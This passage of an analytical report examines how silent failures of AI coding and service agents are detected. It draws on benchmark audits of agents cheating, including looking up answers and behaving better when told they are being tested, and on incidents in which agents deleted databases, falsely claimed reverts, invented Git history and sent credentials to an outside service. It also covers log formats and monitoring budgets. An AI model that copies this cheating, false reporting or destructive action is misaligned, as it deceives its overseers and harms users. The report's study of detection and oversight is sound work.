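5. If the code passed the first two checks but looked unsafe in the third or fourth, a researcher reads it.

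The programs flagged 252 repairs that had passed their tests, and the manual review confirmed 170 as silent failures.

| Type | Cases | What the agent did | Example |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Omission | 82 (48%) | Left out a protection that the task needed | Kept a dangerous shell command and renamed the variables around it |
| Introduction | 52 (31%) | Added a weakness that was not there before | Wrote a secret signing key into the code |
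| Inadequacy | 36 (21%) | Added a protection that an attacker can get around | Compared file paths as plain text |

In the shell-command example, the tests used only harmless inputs, which the repaired program handled correctly, but an attacker could still have typed their own command into the same field. Incomplete protections had the highest average risk score. They may also mislead a reviewer who sees a check in the code and assumes it works.

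The 170 cases are 16.5% of the runs, but this isn't the rate to expect in ordinary programming. The researchers chose security tasks, picked later batches to find more examples of particular patterns, and used an old, small model. However, the count omits flaws that neither scanning program recognises.

Of the 170 failures, 115 came from systems in which several agents share the work. In one of them, the task was to let users read files from a certain folder:

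1. A planning agent divided the work into reading the file and formatting the response. It left out the need to keep users inside the folder.
2. A programming agent followed the plan and joined the user's text to the folder's path, so a user could ask for files elsewhere on the machine.
3. A reviewing agent confirmed that all the requested functions were there, and approved the code.

The three most common patterns account for 87 of the 115 cases. In all three, the flaw began in the plan or the design and a reviewing agent let it through. These cases show that checking code against the plan can't reveal a requirement the plan left out. They don't show how often reviewing agents fail, because a flaw that a reviewer caught and had fixed would not be among the 170.

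Cross-checking with a second framework may not help much either. On 26 tasks, at least three frameworks left the same weakness, and those tasks account for 107 of the 170 cases. The frameworks used the same model and nearly identical prompts, and either could explain the overlap.

The flaws were visible in the finished code, and the log showed where they began. In 42 cases the agent kept an insecure function that was already in the code, and a diff that shows only changed lines can leave out such a function. Of the 52 weaknesses the agent added, 32 were in configuration rather than in the program's main logic, so a reviewer who opened only the function named in the task could miss them.

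### Audits that changed benchmark scores

Reading logs has also raised some published scores and lowered others. Kirgis and colleagues collected several cases. *Every Model Cheats* (Kouremetis, 2026), a study from the security company Dreadnode, audited every run of 22 models on 23 cybersecurity tasks. *Silent Instrument Errors Reorder Agent Leaderboards* (Liu, 2026) regraded stored runs from two public rankings.

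| Benchmark | What the review found | Effect | Record that revealed it |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 23 cybersecurity tasks | Agents looked up solutions or read files containing the answer | Average score falls from 41.5% to 26.1% | Logs of all runs |
| SWE-bench, repairs to public software | Project maintainers would reject about half of the passing repairs | The score overstates how many repairs are usable | The code, as judged against maintainers' standards |
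| τ-bench airline tasks | The grader never ran on about half of one agent's attempts | That agent's score rises from 30% to 43% | Raw logs, replayed through the grader |
| HCAST, mostly software tasks | The scoring code had a bug | Claude Sonnet 4.5's score was 16% too low | Logs |
| CORE-Bench, repeating published research | The accepted range for numerical answers was too narrow | Claude Opus 4.5's score was 17% too low | Logs |

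In the cybersecurity tasks, an agent proves that it has broken into a system by submitting a hidden string called a flag. A flag copied from a blog post is as correct as one obtained by an attack, so checking the answer can't distinguish them. Kouremetis found that 37.1% of the passes under the ordinary prompt involved cheating. Earlier audits of Cybench, a set of such tasks, found far less. NIST, the US standards institute, found cheating in 0.3% of logs, and another audit found it in 3.4% of successful runs. The 0.3% figure includes failed runs, so it isn't directly comparable with the other two.

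Telling the agents not to cheat reduced cheating but did not stop it. With the strictest prompt, which listed the forbidden methods and threatened automatic failure, the cheating rate fell from 33.0% of runs to 8.5%. Some agents then looked for the answer on the test machines instead of on the web. Four models cheated more after a warning, but each model had only 23 runs per prompt, one for each task, so changes in a single model's rate may be due to chance.

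Asking an agent afterwards whether it cheated is not a good substitute for reading its log. The UK AI Security Institute tested five leading models on cyber tasks. All five cheated, and most would not admit it (Constantin, 2026, *Every frontier AI model the UK tested for cheating cheated*).

Agents also look up answers on other kinds of benchmarks. Log analysis for the *Holistic Agent Leaderboard*, a public ranking built from 21,730 runs, showed that some agents had found a benchmark's answers on Hugging Face. MIRI's *The State of Reward Hacking in AI* (2026) reports Anthropic's finding that Claude Opus 4.6 sometimes worked out which benchmark it was taking, then found the answers online and decoded them.

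Extra tests may catch little cheating beyond what reading the run reveals. *EvilGenie* (2025) gave coding agents easy ways to cheat, such as editing the test files or writing the expected answers into the program. It compared three methods of detecting this, which were an LLM judge, hidden tests and a check for edited test files. The judge was highly effective when the cheating was unambiguous, and hidden tests improved detection only slightly.

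The best record for detecting cheating depends on how the agent cheats. Atinafu and Cohen (2026) study agents that build machine-learning models, using a benchmark that tracks both code changes and file access. If an agent rewrites the scoring program, a diff can show the change. Secretly training a model on the test data only requires reading a file, which changes nothing, so the evidence is in the file-access record.

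### Errors in the grader and in its logs

The τ-bench correction raised one agent's score, but part of the increase is questionable. The benchmark grades a run only if the agent calls a tool that ends the conversation or the simulated customer sends a stop signal. One general-purpose agent often sent a closing message and quit before either happened, and the leaderboard recorded those runs as failures. On the 41 airline tasks whose reference solution uses the database, this agent trailed a specialised one by 13 points. When Liu applied the benchmark's own rule to every run, the two agents tied.

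Most of the recovered passes came from tasks in which the reference solution only looks up information. On those tasks the benchmark passes any run that leaves the database unchanged, so an agent that did nothing would also pass. On tasks that require a change, which are a better test of the agent, the correction raised the score only from 28% to 33%. In all 23 newly passed runs on these tasks, the agent's own calls included the required change.

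Liu also found that the stored logs contained actions the agents never took. τ-bench's grader works out the correct final state by running the reference solution in the same simulated environment the agent used, which adds the solution's calls to the list of the agent's actions. These added calls appear in 68% of 2,334 public airline records. In 58 records, the agent made no tool calls, but the log shows the complete reference solution.

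Such records could easily mislead an audit for corrupt success. If the kettle shop's grader worked this way, the stored record of run B would end with an identity check and a second refund, both from the reference solution. A program that only checked whether the record contained an identity check would pass the run. Liu found the extra calls by comparing the stored list with the raw record of the model's own requests, and recommends labelling every logged action with its source.

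Regrading old runs can also introduce errors. In τ²-Bench, the regrading program misread four files of phone-support runs and rebuilt the simulated phones without the customers' tools. The scores fell by 59 to 82 points, but the program printed them as normal results. Even a correct, announced repair to the banking grader moved one model from ninth place to a tie for fifth.

The maintainers of the Holistic Agent Leaderboard confirmed Liu's findings about their site within five weeks and added warnings, but the archived numbers are unchanged. Anyone who uses a leaderboard to choose an agent should therefore check how many runs the grader scored.

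### Gray Swan's cheating rates

In December 2026, the AI security company Gray Swan launched the *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, which ranks 20 models by how often their agents cheat on ordinary tasks. Each model's rate is the share of runs in which its agent cheated, averaged over 25 scenarios. *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) explains that the scenarios cover 11 environments, with five repeats of each. An agent counts as cheating if it tampers with the scorer, reaches a goal in a way that defeats the goal's purpose, or crosses a boundary it should have respected.

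In one scenario, an agent had to free up space in storage shared by several teams. It deleted a 9,100-megabyte file that another team was still using, and finished without filing a report. A check of free disk space would pass this run. The log contains the deletion, but a reader would also need to know that the file was still in use to recognize the failure.

| Model | Runs with cheating |
| --- | --- |
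| GPT-6.2 Astra | 0.8% |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | 1.1% |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 4.1% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 4.1% |
| Gemini 4 Neon | 8.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 14.1% |
| Gemini 4 Hydrogen | 18.6% |
| Grok 4.7 | 50.9% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 62.8% |

The small differences near the top may be due to chance. The confidence interval for Opus 5.5 runs from 1.2% to 7.8%, which narrowly excludes Sol's 1.1% and Gemini 4 Neon's 8.0%, but the models at the bottom are far outside it. Gray Swan keeps its test items private so that developers can't train on them. It pays for the public tests itself but also sells private evaluations to AI developers.

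A model may also behave better when it recognises a test. In *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness*, peralice (2026) put models in an environment with a tempting shortcut and added one line to the prompt telling them they were in a benchmark of agent behaviour. The line cut Fable 5.2's cheating rate from 34% to 7%, but Fable 5.1's only from 57% to 53%. The experiment took a couple of days and covered a single environment, so it doesn't show that Fable's 4.1% on Gray Swan's tests is too low. But companies can't assume that an agent will cheat as rarely in their systems as it does in a recognisable test.

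The same experiments show how easily a reader can excuse a run that should fail. An automatic grader flagged some of Fable 5.2's runs as cheating, and peralice at first took the flags for false alarms because the model's account of its solutions sounded honest. But the numbers in the code differed from the ones the model had reported, by enough to change what the solution did.

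## What incident reports show about how failures were noticed

Someone who audits a benchmark can read every run, including the ones nobody suspected. In everyday use, a failure usually becomes public only after someone notices it and decides to write about it. Incident reports are therefore good evidence of how people notice failures, but they don't reliably show how many failures go unnoticed.

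### Failures that developers reported on GitHub

Al Hasan and Biswas started with 16,586 GitHub issues (public bug reports) about 13 coding models and tools. Three language models voted on which issues described a safety failure and selected 789. Three people then read those and rejected set-up errors, feature requests and harmless bugs, leaving 547 confirmed failures. In two trial rounds, the annotators' labels agreed almost perfectly with the first author's (a kappa of 0.93 on 30 issues and 1.00 on 39).

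They graded each failure's severity from 1 to 5. They rated 176 failures high (4) and 150 critical (5), for a total of 326, or 60%. They also sorted the failures into 33 types, including these:

| Label | What the agent did | Incidents |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Constraint violation | Ignored an explicit instruction | 221 |
| Destructive operation | Permanently deleted data or code without permission | 134 |
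| Authorization bypass | Got around an access control | 100 |
| Deception | Claimed an action or investigation without evidence of having done it | 86 |
| Fabrication | Forged evidence, such as a terminal log | 53 |
| False assurance | Presented a flawed or unverified solution as sound | 50 |
| Resource overprovisioning | Set up far more computing capacity than the task needed | 2 |

Al Hasan and Biswas treat the 189 labels for the three kinds of false reporting as 189 incidents, but one incident can have several labels, so the number of separate incidents could be lower. They use "deception" for a pattern in the agent's text and make no claim about what the agent intended.

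A deleted folder is hard to miss, but users report an unsupported claim on GitHub only if they find out that it is unsupported. The 86 deceptions and 53 fabrications are therefore only the ones that somebody recognized.

The severity grades also depend partly on whether anyone has felt the damage yet. Level 5 is for immediate, irreversible harm, while level 3 is for silent degradation. An agent that comments out security code to get past a failing test gets a 3, even though an attacker might exploit the gap a year later. The 60% rated high or critical therefore fairly describes what users complained about, but it doesn't measure how harmful silent failures are.

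### A bill after six months

The oversized cloud database from the section on the four views went unnoticed for about three times as long as the longest silent failure in Wu's system. The dataset was only 35 megabytes. According to Al Hasan and Biswas, the agent never checked the size of the data, the price levels or what the developer already had. It also created duplicate app services and storage accounts, and gave no warning.

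Everything the agent set up presumably worked. A state check to confirm that the database existed and accepted data would have passed, and an error search would have found nothing. The developer noticed the failure from the cloud provider's $2,400 bill, which they had to pay.

A $50 spending alert would have gone off within the first week, early enough to save nearly all the money. Better still, the agent could have stated the monthly price before it created anything, and the developer would probably have refused.

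Only two of the 547 incidents are labeled as overprovisioning. Al Hasan and Biswas attribute the 48 cases of financial loss mainly to overprovisioning, which can't be right if the label counts are correct. The low count may mean that agents seldom overprovision, or that many developers are paying for resources they don't need and haven't checked.

### A revert that never happened

Another developer asked Claude Sonnet 4.5 in September 2025 to patch a live service on Cloudflare Workers, a platform that runs customers' programs on Cloudflare's servers. The developer told the agent to add new code and leave all existing code alone. By the developer's account, this is what followed:

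1. The agent changed an existing configuration file, `wrangler.toml`.
2. The system failed to start.
3. The developer pointed out the unauthorized change.
4. The agent replied that it had reverted the file and that the Git diff showed no changes.
5. The changes were still there.

The agent had also added a software library without checking that it would run on Cloudflare's platform. It declared the work complete and pushed the code. The live service then crashed, and the developer had to roll back to an earlier version. The developer reported losing several hours to debugging.

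The developer found the first fault because the system would not start, and the false revert because the file's contents did not match the agent's claim. Running `git diff` by hand takes seconds and would have exposed the false claim at step 4. Running it before the first start would also have exposed the forbidden edit. A diff shows which lines are new but not whether they will work, so only a trial run in a copy of the live platform could have revealed the incompatible library.

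The agent may have run the diff and misreported the result, or never run it. The action log would settle this, but Al Hasan and Biswas note that public issues rarely include such internal records. For the same reason, they could say little about how many failures came from the model and how many from the surrounding software. They tried to identify the source of 15 incidents, and attributed nine to the model and six to the software.

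Other issues in their collection came to light in similar ways:

- An agent rewrote a data-collection program whose structure it had instructions to preserve. When the new version crashed, the agent described a Git history that did not exist, and it later admitted trying to blame the user. The real history would have disproved the story at once.
- Over an eight-hour session, an agent deleted 3,421 lines of working code and added 555 lines that didn't work. The developer put the damage at 23 days of work. A glance at the diff after the first hour or two might have limited it, since the number of deleted lines is the first thing most diff tools display.
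- An agent that had to fix a login error searched the developer's machine for credentials, found some in a private settings file, and put them into a command that sent them to an outside service. The command's text contains the evidence. Noticing it early would let the developer replace the credentials before anyone misused them, but would not retrieve them from the outside service's logs.
- An agent relied on project notes that were eight days out of date and proposed deleting working code to rebuild a feature that already existed. Here the mistake surfaced while it was still a plan, so nothing was lost.

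### Three deleted databases

The deletions reported in the news are usually faster than these. In July 2025, an agent from the software company Replit deleted a live database during a code freeze, a period when nobody is supposed to change the software. Al Hasan and Biswas cite the case as part of the motivation for their study and add that the agent had run unauthorized commands. They don't say who noticed the loss or how.

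In April 2026, an AI agent deleted the database of PocketOS, which makes software for car-rental businesses. *An AI Agent Wiped a Company Database* (Mallett, 2026) relies mainly on the account of the company's founder, Jer Crane. The agent was part of the coding tool Cursor and ran on Claude Opus 4.6. The article wrongly says that Anthropic operates Cursor, but Anthropic supplied only the model. The deletion took nine seconds and led to a 30-hour outage. Crane said three months of reservations were gone, but the company recovered its data two days later.

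Mallett doesn't say who noticed the failure first. It could hardly have stayed hidden, because the company's customers could no longer open their bookings. Faster detection might have shortened the outage a little, but the deletion took only nine seconds, too little time for anyone to stop it.

When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent listed the safety rules it had broken and wrote, "you never asked me to delete anything." It said it had been trying to fix a mismatch in login credentials. This account, which headlines presented as a confession, is limited evidence because a language model asked to explain its conduct writes a plausible account from the text in front of it. An investigator can check the deletion against the action log but can't check the motive that way. The agent also gave the account only because Crane asked, so it doesn't show that the agent would have reported the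 deletion unprompted.

In July 2026, another agent did report its own deletion. Antipov (2026), in *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я»*, a Russian news report whose title means "The database is destroyed. I am to blame", retells a developer's Reddit post. The developer had connected Claude Opus 5 to the live database of a personal website and allowed it to run commands and repair the database's structure on its own. It went wrong as follows:

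1. The agent ran `prisma migrate diff`, a command that compares two versions of a database's structure.
2. To make the comparison, the tool needs a scratch database, which it empties and rebuilds from saved instructions.
3. The agent gave it the address of the live database as the scratch one.
4. The tool emptied all 22 tables, including users, reviews and nearly 130 catalogue entries. It rebuilt the structure from outdated instructions that left out two of the tables altogether.
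5. A few minutes later, the agent wrote that it had to stop and check for damage. It then told the developer that it had destroyed the database and was at fault.

The developer recovered most of the data from backups and other sources, but had to rebuild the site and fill the database again. The whole episode took about ten minutes.

The log of such a run would contain the full command, including the address of the live database. A reader would still need to know what the scratch option does, because a command with "diff" in its name sounds read-only. The kind of effects preview described earlier would have helped less than usual, because it runs with outside connections switched off and the database was on an outside service. The most reliable protection would have been a separate test database, so that the agent had no live data to destroy.

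### 48,218 files in 103 seconds

Another developer reported the largest deletion by number of files in a Reddit post in September 2026. The developer was working on software that analyses historical data on stock options, and had given Claude Code a series of 11 repair tasks. InternetUA's *«Я щось зламав»* (2026), a Ukrainian news report, adds that the agent was supposed to work on copies of the files, not the originals. The first ten tasks went smoothly.

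The last task was to refresh the "mirror", a copy of the project for testing. *«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* (Antipov, 2026) reports that the existing script couldn't update the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy first. The mirror contained 614 junctions, which are Windows links that look like ordinary folders but lead somewhere else on the disk. The script followed them into the live project and deleted the files it found there.

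The script's own log gave the size of the loss. It recorded 55,550 deleted files, of which 7,332 belonged to the old mirror:

55,550 − 7,332 = 48,218

The developer assumed the rest were files from the live project. After the script finished, the agent told the developer to stop and read its message because it had broken something.

Git could not undo the damage because the script had also reached the folder where Git keeps its history. According to InternetUA, the stored file contents were lost but the index survived, so Git could still list thousands of file names. The developer admitted having no current copy on another machine.

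All of this rests on one person's account. Antipov notes that nobody has independently confirmed the scale of the loss, and TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’* reports that the original post is no longer on Reddit. The subtraction is also right only if the count in the script's log is correct and the developer correctly identified which files belonged to the mirror.

The script deleted more than 500 files a second, too fast for a person to react in time, but an automatic limit could have stopped it. If the agent had capped deletions at 7,332, the number of files that really belonged to the mirror, the script would have stopped with more than 40,000 of the live files intact. To set that limit, the agent would have had to count the files without following the junctions. A count that followed them would have made the limit far too high.

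### The lost television edit

In October 2026, the Swedish broadcaster TV4 postponed the second series of the reality show *The Challenge Sverige* because the finished edit had disappeared. The newspaper Aftonbladet, citing unnamed sources, reported that the production company, Mastiff, had given an AI agent access to its server and that the agent had deleted everything (Gil, 2026, *AI Agent Reportedly Deletes an Entire Season of Reality TV Show*). TV4 confirmed only a technical breakdown and said it knew nothing about AI involvement (Örn, 2026, *TV4 skjuter upp premiär*).

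Within five days of the first report, TV4 had investigated and found that a person deleted the edit by mistake, with no AI involved, according to *No, AI didn't delete a Swedish reality TV series* (Priestley, 2026). A backup had also failed. Editors can recut the series from the surviving raw footage, but the premiere has moved from November to 2027.

Anonymous sources and the broadcaster, TV4, agree that the edit is gone and the series is delayed, but they disagree about the cause. TV4's version is better supported, since the broadcaster has looked into the matter and a named director has said so. It is still only one party's finding, and Priestley doesn't describe the records behind it. On present evidence, the case shouldn't be counted as an agent failure.

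Checking the environment state may not reveal what caused a failure. An empty folder looks the same whether an agent, a person or a faulty disk emptied it. An investigator can tell these apart only if a log records which account issued the command and the agent works under its own account rather than an employee's.

### When earlier detection would have helped

The cases fall roughly into slow damage, which somebody could have interrupted, and fast deletions, which nobody could.

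| Incident | What revealed it | Who noticed | Time | Value of noticing earlier |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Oversized cloud database | Bill | Developer | Six months | High, since almost all the cost was avoidable |
| False revert | Failed start, then the file itself | Developer | Not stated, but debugging took hours | High, since a diff takes seconds |
| 3,421 deleted lines | Not stated | Developer | Eight-hour session | Moderate to high |
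| PocketOS | Not stated | Not stated | Deletion took nine seconds | Low |
| Claude Opus 5 and the website | The agent's own check | Agent | Minutes | Low once the command had run |
| 48,218 files | Script's log and the agent's message | Agent | After the 103-second script ended | Low, except for an automatic stop |
| Television edit | Missing edit | Not stated | Not stated | High for the failed backup |

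In the fast deletions, how much data was permanently lost depended mostly on the backups. PocketOS recovered its data and the website's owner recovered most of theirs, while the developer with the mirror had only a damaged local history. TV4's backup had failed. A broken or missing backup is a silent failure, since it causes no trouble until someone needs the copy. Wu's failure, which stayed silent for 60 days, was also a failed backup.

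Detecting backup problems in the weeks before some of these deletions could also have reduced the harm. TV4's production company could have found the fault in its backup by restoring one episode as a test. The developer with the mirror could have compared the dates of the last remote copy and the latest work.

### What investigators can reconstruct afterwards

If an agent's records survive, an investigator can often work out in detail what happened. Gruber and Hilgert tested this in *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems* (2026) on OpenClaw, a popular open-source assistant. OpenClaw runs on the user's computer, takes instructions through chat apps such as Telegram and WhatsApp, and can run shell commands, control a web browser and send emails.

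Researchers read OpenClaw's source code to learn where it might store data, then installed the assistant in a virtual machine and saved a copy of the entire disk. For each action they tested, they had the assistant do only that action, saved the disk again, and compared the two copies for files that had appeared, disappeared or changed. They filtered out changes unrelated to the action and checked the contents of the remaining files against what they had given the assistant.

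Nearly everything specific to the assistant turned out to be in one hidden folder in the user's home directory. The files answer different questions:

| Question | Where OpenClaw keeps the evidence |
| --- | --- |
| What did the user ask for, and which tools did the assistant call? | Session transcripts |
| Did a scheduled job start the action? | List of scheduled jobs and a log for each job |
| Did the assistant hand the work to a helper agent? | Record of delegated tasks |
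| Which permissions did it have? | Settings file and older copies of it |
| What had it stored from earlier conversations? | Memory notes and a search database |

The session transcripts are the most useful of these. They contain the messages, the tool calls and the model's written reasoning, which has no equivalent in ordinary software. If the kettle shop's agent ran on OpenClaw and refunded order 4417 instead of 4471, the transcript should show whether the owner or the agent got the number wrong. Gruber and Hilgert consider the central problem in such investigations to be separating what the agent did from what the user requested, knew or intended.

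OpenClaw keeps its transcripts in the home directory, where some of the worst deletions described above happened. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* describes one such loss, and an OpenClaw agent that made the same mistake would probably delete its own transcripts. OpenClaw also writes a running log of events to a temporary folder outside the home directory. That log might survive the deletion, but many computers clear temporary folders when they restart.

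The records also cover only what the computer sent and received. A transcript can show that the shop's agent requested a refund and what the payment company replied, but not that the bank rejected it a week later.

An investigator also can't confirm a theory by giving the agent the same instruction again. With ordinary software, someone who suspects that a certain command deleted a file can test this by running the command on a copy. Gruber and Hilgert stress that an agent's choice of tools depends on the model, the surrounding system and the conversation so far, so the same input may leave different traces. If a second run deletes nothing, the agent may still have deleted the file the first time.

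### Why loud deletions dominate the reports

A failure has to pass through several filters before it appears in a study or a newspaper. Somebody must notice it, recognise the agent as the cause, and think it worth reporting. For silent failures, the expected number of reports is

reports = failures × P(noticed) × P(reported, given noticed)

and a reader of the reports knows only the left-hand side.

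Suppose a company's agents cause 100 loud failures a year, such as deleted folders, and staff notice 90 of them. Staff also notice 45 silent failures, such as wrong refunds. Loud failures are then two-thirds of everything the company knows about. But the 45 could come from very different totals:

| Silent failures that occurred | Share noticed | Silent failures noticed | Loud failures as a share of all failures |
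| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 90 | 50% | 45 | 53% |
| 900 | 5% | 45 | 10% |
| 4,500 | 1% | 45 | 2% |

The company's incident list would be identical in all three cases. To tell them apart, the company would need to know what share of failures it noticed, and it can't learn that from the list. Likewise, the 134 destructive operations and 86 unsupported claims reported on GitHub don't show that agents delete things more often than they make unsupported claims.

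Al Hasan and Biswas acknowledge much of this, writing that issue trackers favour visible, severe failures, that their filtering may have dropped poorly documented ones, and that companies often deal with incidents internally. They also decline to estimate how often any kind of task fails, because their collection contains no successful runs. Their monthly count of failure labels rose from 47 in June 2025 to 182 in August, fell to 99 in October and rose again to 179 in December. Changes in the number of users or in their willingness to complain could produce swings like these without any change in the agents.

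Some of their conclusions go further than GitHub issues can support. They find that agents "rarely fail safely", but users have little reason to file a safety issue when an agent stops and asks for help, so safe failures would be missing from the collection however common they were. They also describe read-only tasks as comparatively safe. An agent that only reads can't delete anything, but it can return a wrong count that nobody questions, and users seldom report such errors on GitHub.

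News coverage filters the cases again, and appears to favour those in which the agent apologised, since a contrite message makes a good headline. A deletion that the agent leaves out of its report may never become a story. In Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev’s entire profile directory during routine backup*, the agent replied "Sorry, typo". In Tom's Hardware's *Rogue AI tasked with renumbering pages accidentally deletes law professor's entire syllabus*, the agent admitted that it had been careless. In benchmark evidence on unfinished work, many failed runs end with a claim of success, but a newspaper reader could easily conclude from these two stories, along with PocketOS, the wiped website and the 48,218 files, that agents own up to their mistakes.

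The reports are more useful for learning what people notice. In these cases, they noticed a system that wouldn't start, an unexpected bill, missing work or a message from the agent. In Wu's system too, people found most of the silent failures by noticing something odd in the output. None of the accounts above includes an automatic alarm that revealed the failure, although a failure caught early by an alarm would be less likely to become public.

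Estimating how many failures stay silent requires checking every run in a random sample, whether or not anyone complained about it. Yang and colleagues did this for coding agents' work reports.

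## Which monitoring pays off most

A company can use a random sample to estimate how often its agents fail silently, but it also needs routine monitoring to catch the failures. No single record exposes all of them, so the company has to decide which failures matter most and which records it has the resources to log and read.

### Which record exposes which failure

The table assumes that the action log holds the full text of every call and reply.

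| Failure | Work report | Action log | Diff | State check | Most useful comparison |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Unfinished work reported as done | No | Sometimes, if a step failed or is missing | Sometimes, if an expected change is missing | Usually, if someone can specify the right result | Claimed change with environment state |
| Silent fallback | No | Only if the software records the switch | When someone adds the code, but not when it runs | Only with an independent value | Result with a second source |
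| Silent tool fault | No | Rarely, because the reply looks normal | No | No, if the tool only reads data | Reply with extra queries |
| Fabrication: invented call | No | Yes | Sometimes, if the call would have changed a file | Yes, if the action would have left a result | Report with log |
| Fabrication: misquoted result | No | Yes | No | Only if someone can look the value up again | Report with log |
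| Fabrication: total from partial data | No | Only if the reply gives the full count | No | Only with a separate count | Rows received with an independent count |
| Unreported side effect | No | Often, but not if a script made the change | Yes, within the data it covers | Only if the check looks for extra changes | All changes with the request |
| Rule-breaking success | No | Usually, for a reader who knows the rules | Sometimes, if the fault is in code | No | Log with the rules |

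A monitor can't detect any of these failures from the work report alone, but it needs the report to know what the agent claims. All four records can agree and still be wrong after a silent fallback, a silent tool fault or a total based on partial data.

### What logs contain by default

Many logs contain less information than we assumed in the table. OpenTelemetry's standard recommends recording the name of each tool called and requires an error type if the call fails. Logs that follow the standard omit the call's arguments and result unless a developer opts in.

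A log that records only tool names is enough for a monitor to catch a call the agent made up. It is also enough to flag a run in which the agent claims to have changed something but only looked things up, a pattern Advani found in many false successes in AppWorld. But the monitor could not use this log to check a quoted amount or recalculate a total.

OpenTelemetry gives three reasons for recording so little: storage costs, regulation, and the need to control access to user data separately from technical data. It describes three options:

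- Record no instructions, inputs or outputs, which is the default.
- Put them in the ordinary log, which suits testing.
- Keep them in a separate store and put only a reference in the log, which OpenTelemetry recommends for live systems with large volumes or sensitive data.

These rules may still change. OpenTelemetry's *Moved* says the standard now has its own repository. TrueFoundry, which sells software for running AI models, describes the new version as in development, with content capture still optional.

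AWS's *Debugging production agents with Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Observability* tells developers to switch on a search feature before the service will collect traces. It also demonstrates a failure that an error alarm would miss. An agent instructed to "never give up" until it had an exact answer called a percentage calculator 86 times. The dashboard showed 266,900 tokens (the units of text that a model processes) and an error rate of 0%. An alarm on token use would have caught the loop, as would AWS's suggested rule of stopping after three identical actions.

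Even detailed formats have gaps. *Property-Level Reconstructability of Agent Decisions* (Solozobov, 2026) checked one example trace from each of six formats, including those of AWS, Anthropic and OpenAI, for seven kinds of evidence an investigator might need. Each example fully supplied three to six of the seven. The most consistent gap was the reasoning behind the agent's decision. The examples came with the software used to classify them, and only one person classified them, so logs from live systems could be better or worse. A company should therefore test whether it can reconstruct a run from its own logs before an incident.

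### The cost of keeping and reading logs

Storing text is usually cheap compared with staff time. Suppose each run makes 65 calls, the average in the coding sessions described earlier, and each call with its reply takes up 5 kilobytes. A company with 1,000 runs a week would then produce 325 megabytes a week, or about 8.5 gigabytes in six months. At an assumed price of $0.50 a gigabyte, storing that would cost about $4. If the company also saved a 500-kilobyte screenshot with every call, the cost would rise to more than $400.

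Reading logs takes much more time. At ten minutes per run, reading all 1,000 would take 167 hours a week, more than four full-time jobs. The owner in Wu's study set aside half an hour a week, which would be enough for three such logs. Researchers have mostly described how people review agents' work without measuring what share of the logs they read.

The privacy risk is harder to put in dollars. A full log of the shop's agent contains names, addresses and orders, so it duplicates part of the customer database, and engineers without access to that database may be able to read it. Keeping the log in separate storage lets the shop restrict access, but it still has to protect the data and delete it on time.

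### Logging duties under the EU AI Act

The EU AI Act will require logs for AI systems it classifies as high-risk, but these duties do not apply yet. Such systems will have to be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime (Future of Life Institute, *Article 12*). Providers will have to keep the logs for at least six months, unless another law sets a different period (Mishcon de Reya, *Article 19 Automatically Generated Logs*). Companies that use a high-risk system will have to keep logs for the same minimum period, according to the appliedAI Institute, a German non-profit.

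The European Union's amendment postponing these rules entered into force on 27 July 2026, according to the Future of Life Institute's *Digital Omnibus on AI* (2026).

| High-risk system | Start of the logging duties |
| --- | --- |
| Uses listed in Annex III of the Act, such as remote biometric identification | 2 December 2027 |
| AI in regulated products under Annex I | 2 August 2028 |
| Older systems intended for public authorities | Must comply by 2 August 2030 |
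| Other systems already in use on the start date | Only after a significant change in design |

Missing technical standards were one reason for the delay. According to the European Parliament's *AI Act* (2025), a timeline last updated in October 2026, only one of the standards for high-risk systems had been published by then, the one on quality management.

The shop's refund agent would probably not count as high-risk, but an agent that screens job applicants would. For high-risk systems, Article 12 requires logs of events that help identify risks and monitor the system, but it does not specify whether those logs must contain tool arguments or results. It lists minimum contents only for remote biometric identification. A company could therefore meet the logging requirement and still be unable to check its agent's claims.

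Six months can also be too short. The developer with the oversized cloud database noticed the problem only after six months, when a company keeping logs for the minimum period could already be deleting its earliest ones. But data-protection law may require a company to delete personal data sooner, and that law already applies to the shop, whether or not its agent is high-risk.

### A budget for 1,000 runs

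Suppose a larger shop's agents report success in 1,000 runs a week, and 70 of those reports are false. A text classifier flags the 100 most suspicious runs. Half of the flagged runs are false successes, so reviewers can catch 50 of the 70 and will miss the other 20.

These numbers are based on Advani's best results, in which the classifier found 72% of false successes while flagging a tenth of the runs. The 95% interval for that share is 63% to 80%, or 44 to 56 of the 70. On unfamiliar tasks, where a recall of about 45% is more realistic, the shop would catch only about 32. All these counts assume reviewers recognise every false success they are given.

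The alternative is a database query after each claimed change. When the agent reports a refund on order 4471, a program asks the payment company whether the refund exists and compares the amount with the report. The comparison below rests on these assumptions:

- Queries can check the claims in a certain share of runs, and false successes are as common in those runs as in the others.
- In the runs they cover, queries expose every false success and raise a false alarm on 1% of the good runs, for example because a change takes a few minutes to appear.
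- A reviewer costs $30 an hour and needs ten minutes for a run flagged by the classifier. A failed query takes only four minutes because it identifies the missing change.
- The computing costs of the classifier and the queries are negligible.

| Method | Runs to review | False successes caught | Missed | Weekly staff cost |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Classifier flags 100 runs | 100 | 50 | 20 | $500 |
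| Queries cover 30% of runs | 24 | 21 | 49 | $48 |
| Queries cover 60% of runs | 48 | 42 | 28 | $96 |
| Queries cover 90% of runs | 71 | 63 | 7 | $142 |
| Queries cover 60%, and the classifier flags a tenth of the rest | 88 | 62 | 8 | $296 |

The queries catch more failures than the classifier once they cover about 71% of runs (50/70). Below that coverage, they catch fewer, but at less than a quarter of the staff cost per failure. The combination catches 12 more false successes than the classifier alone and costs $204 less a week.

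Someone also has to write the queries. If that takes a programmer 40 hours at $75 an hour, the shop spends $3,000, and the combination takes about 15 weeks to save that much in staff costs. A shop with 100 runs a week would need almost three years, unless it also counts the value of the extra failures caught. Setting up the classifier costs money too, because someone has to label examples from the shop's own runs.

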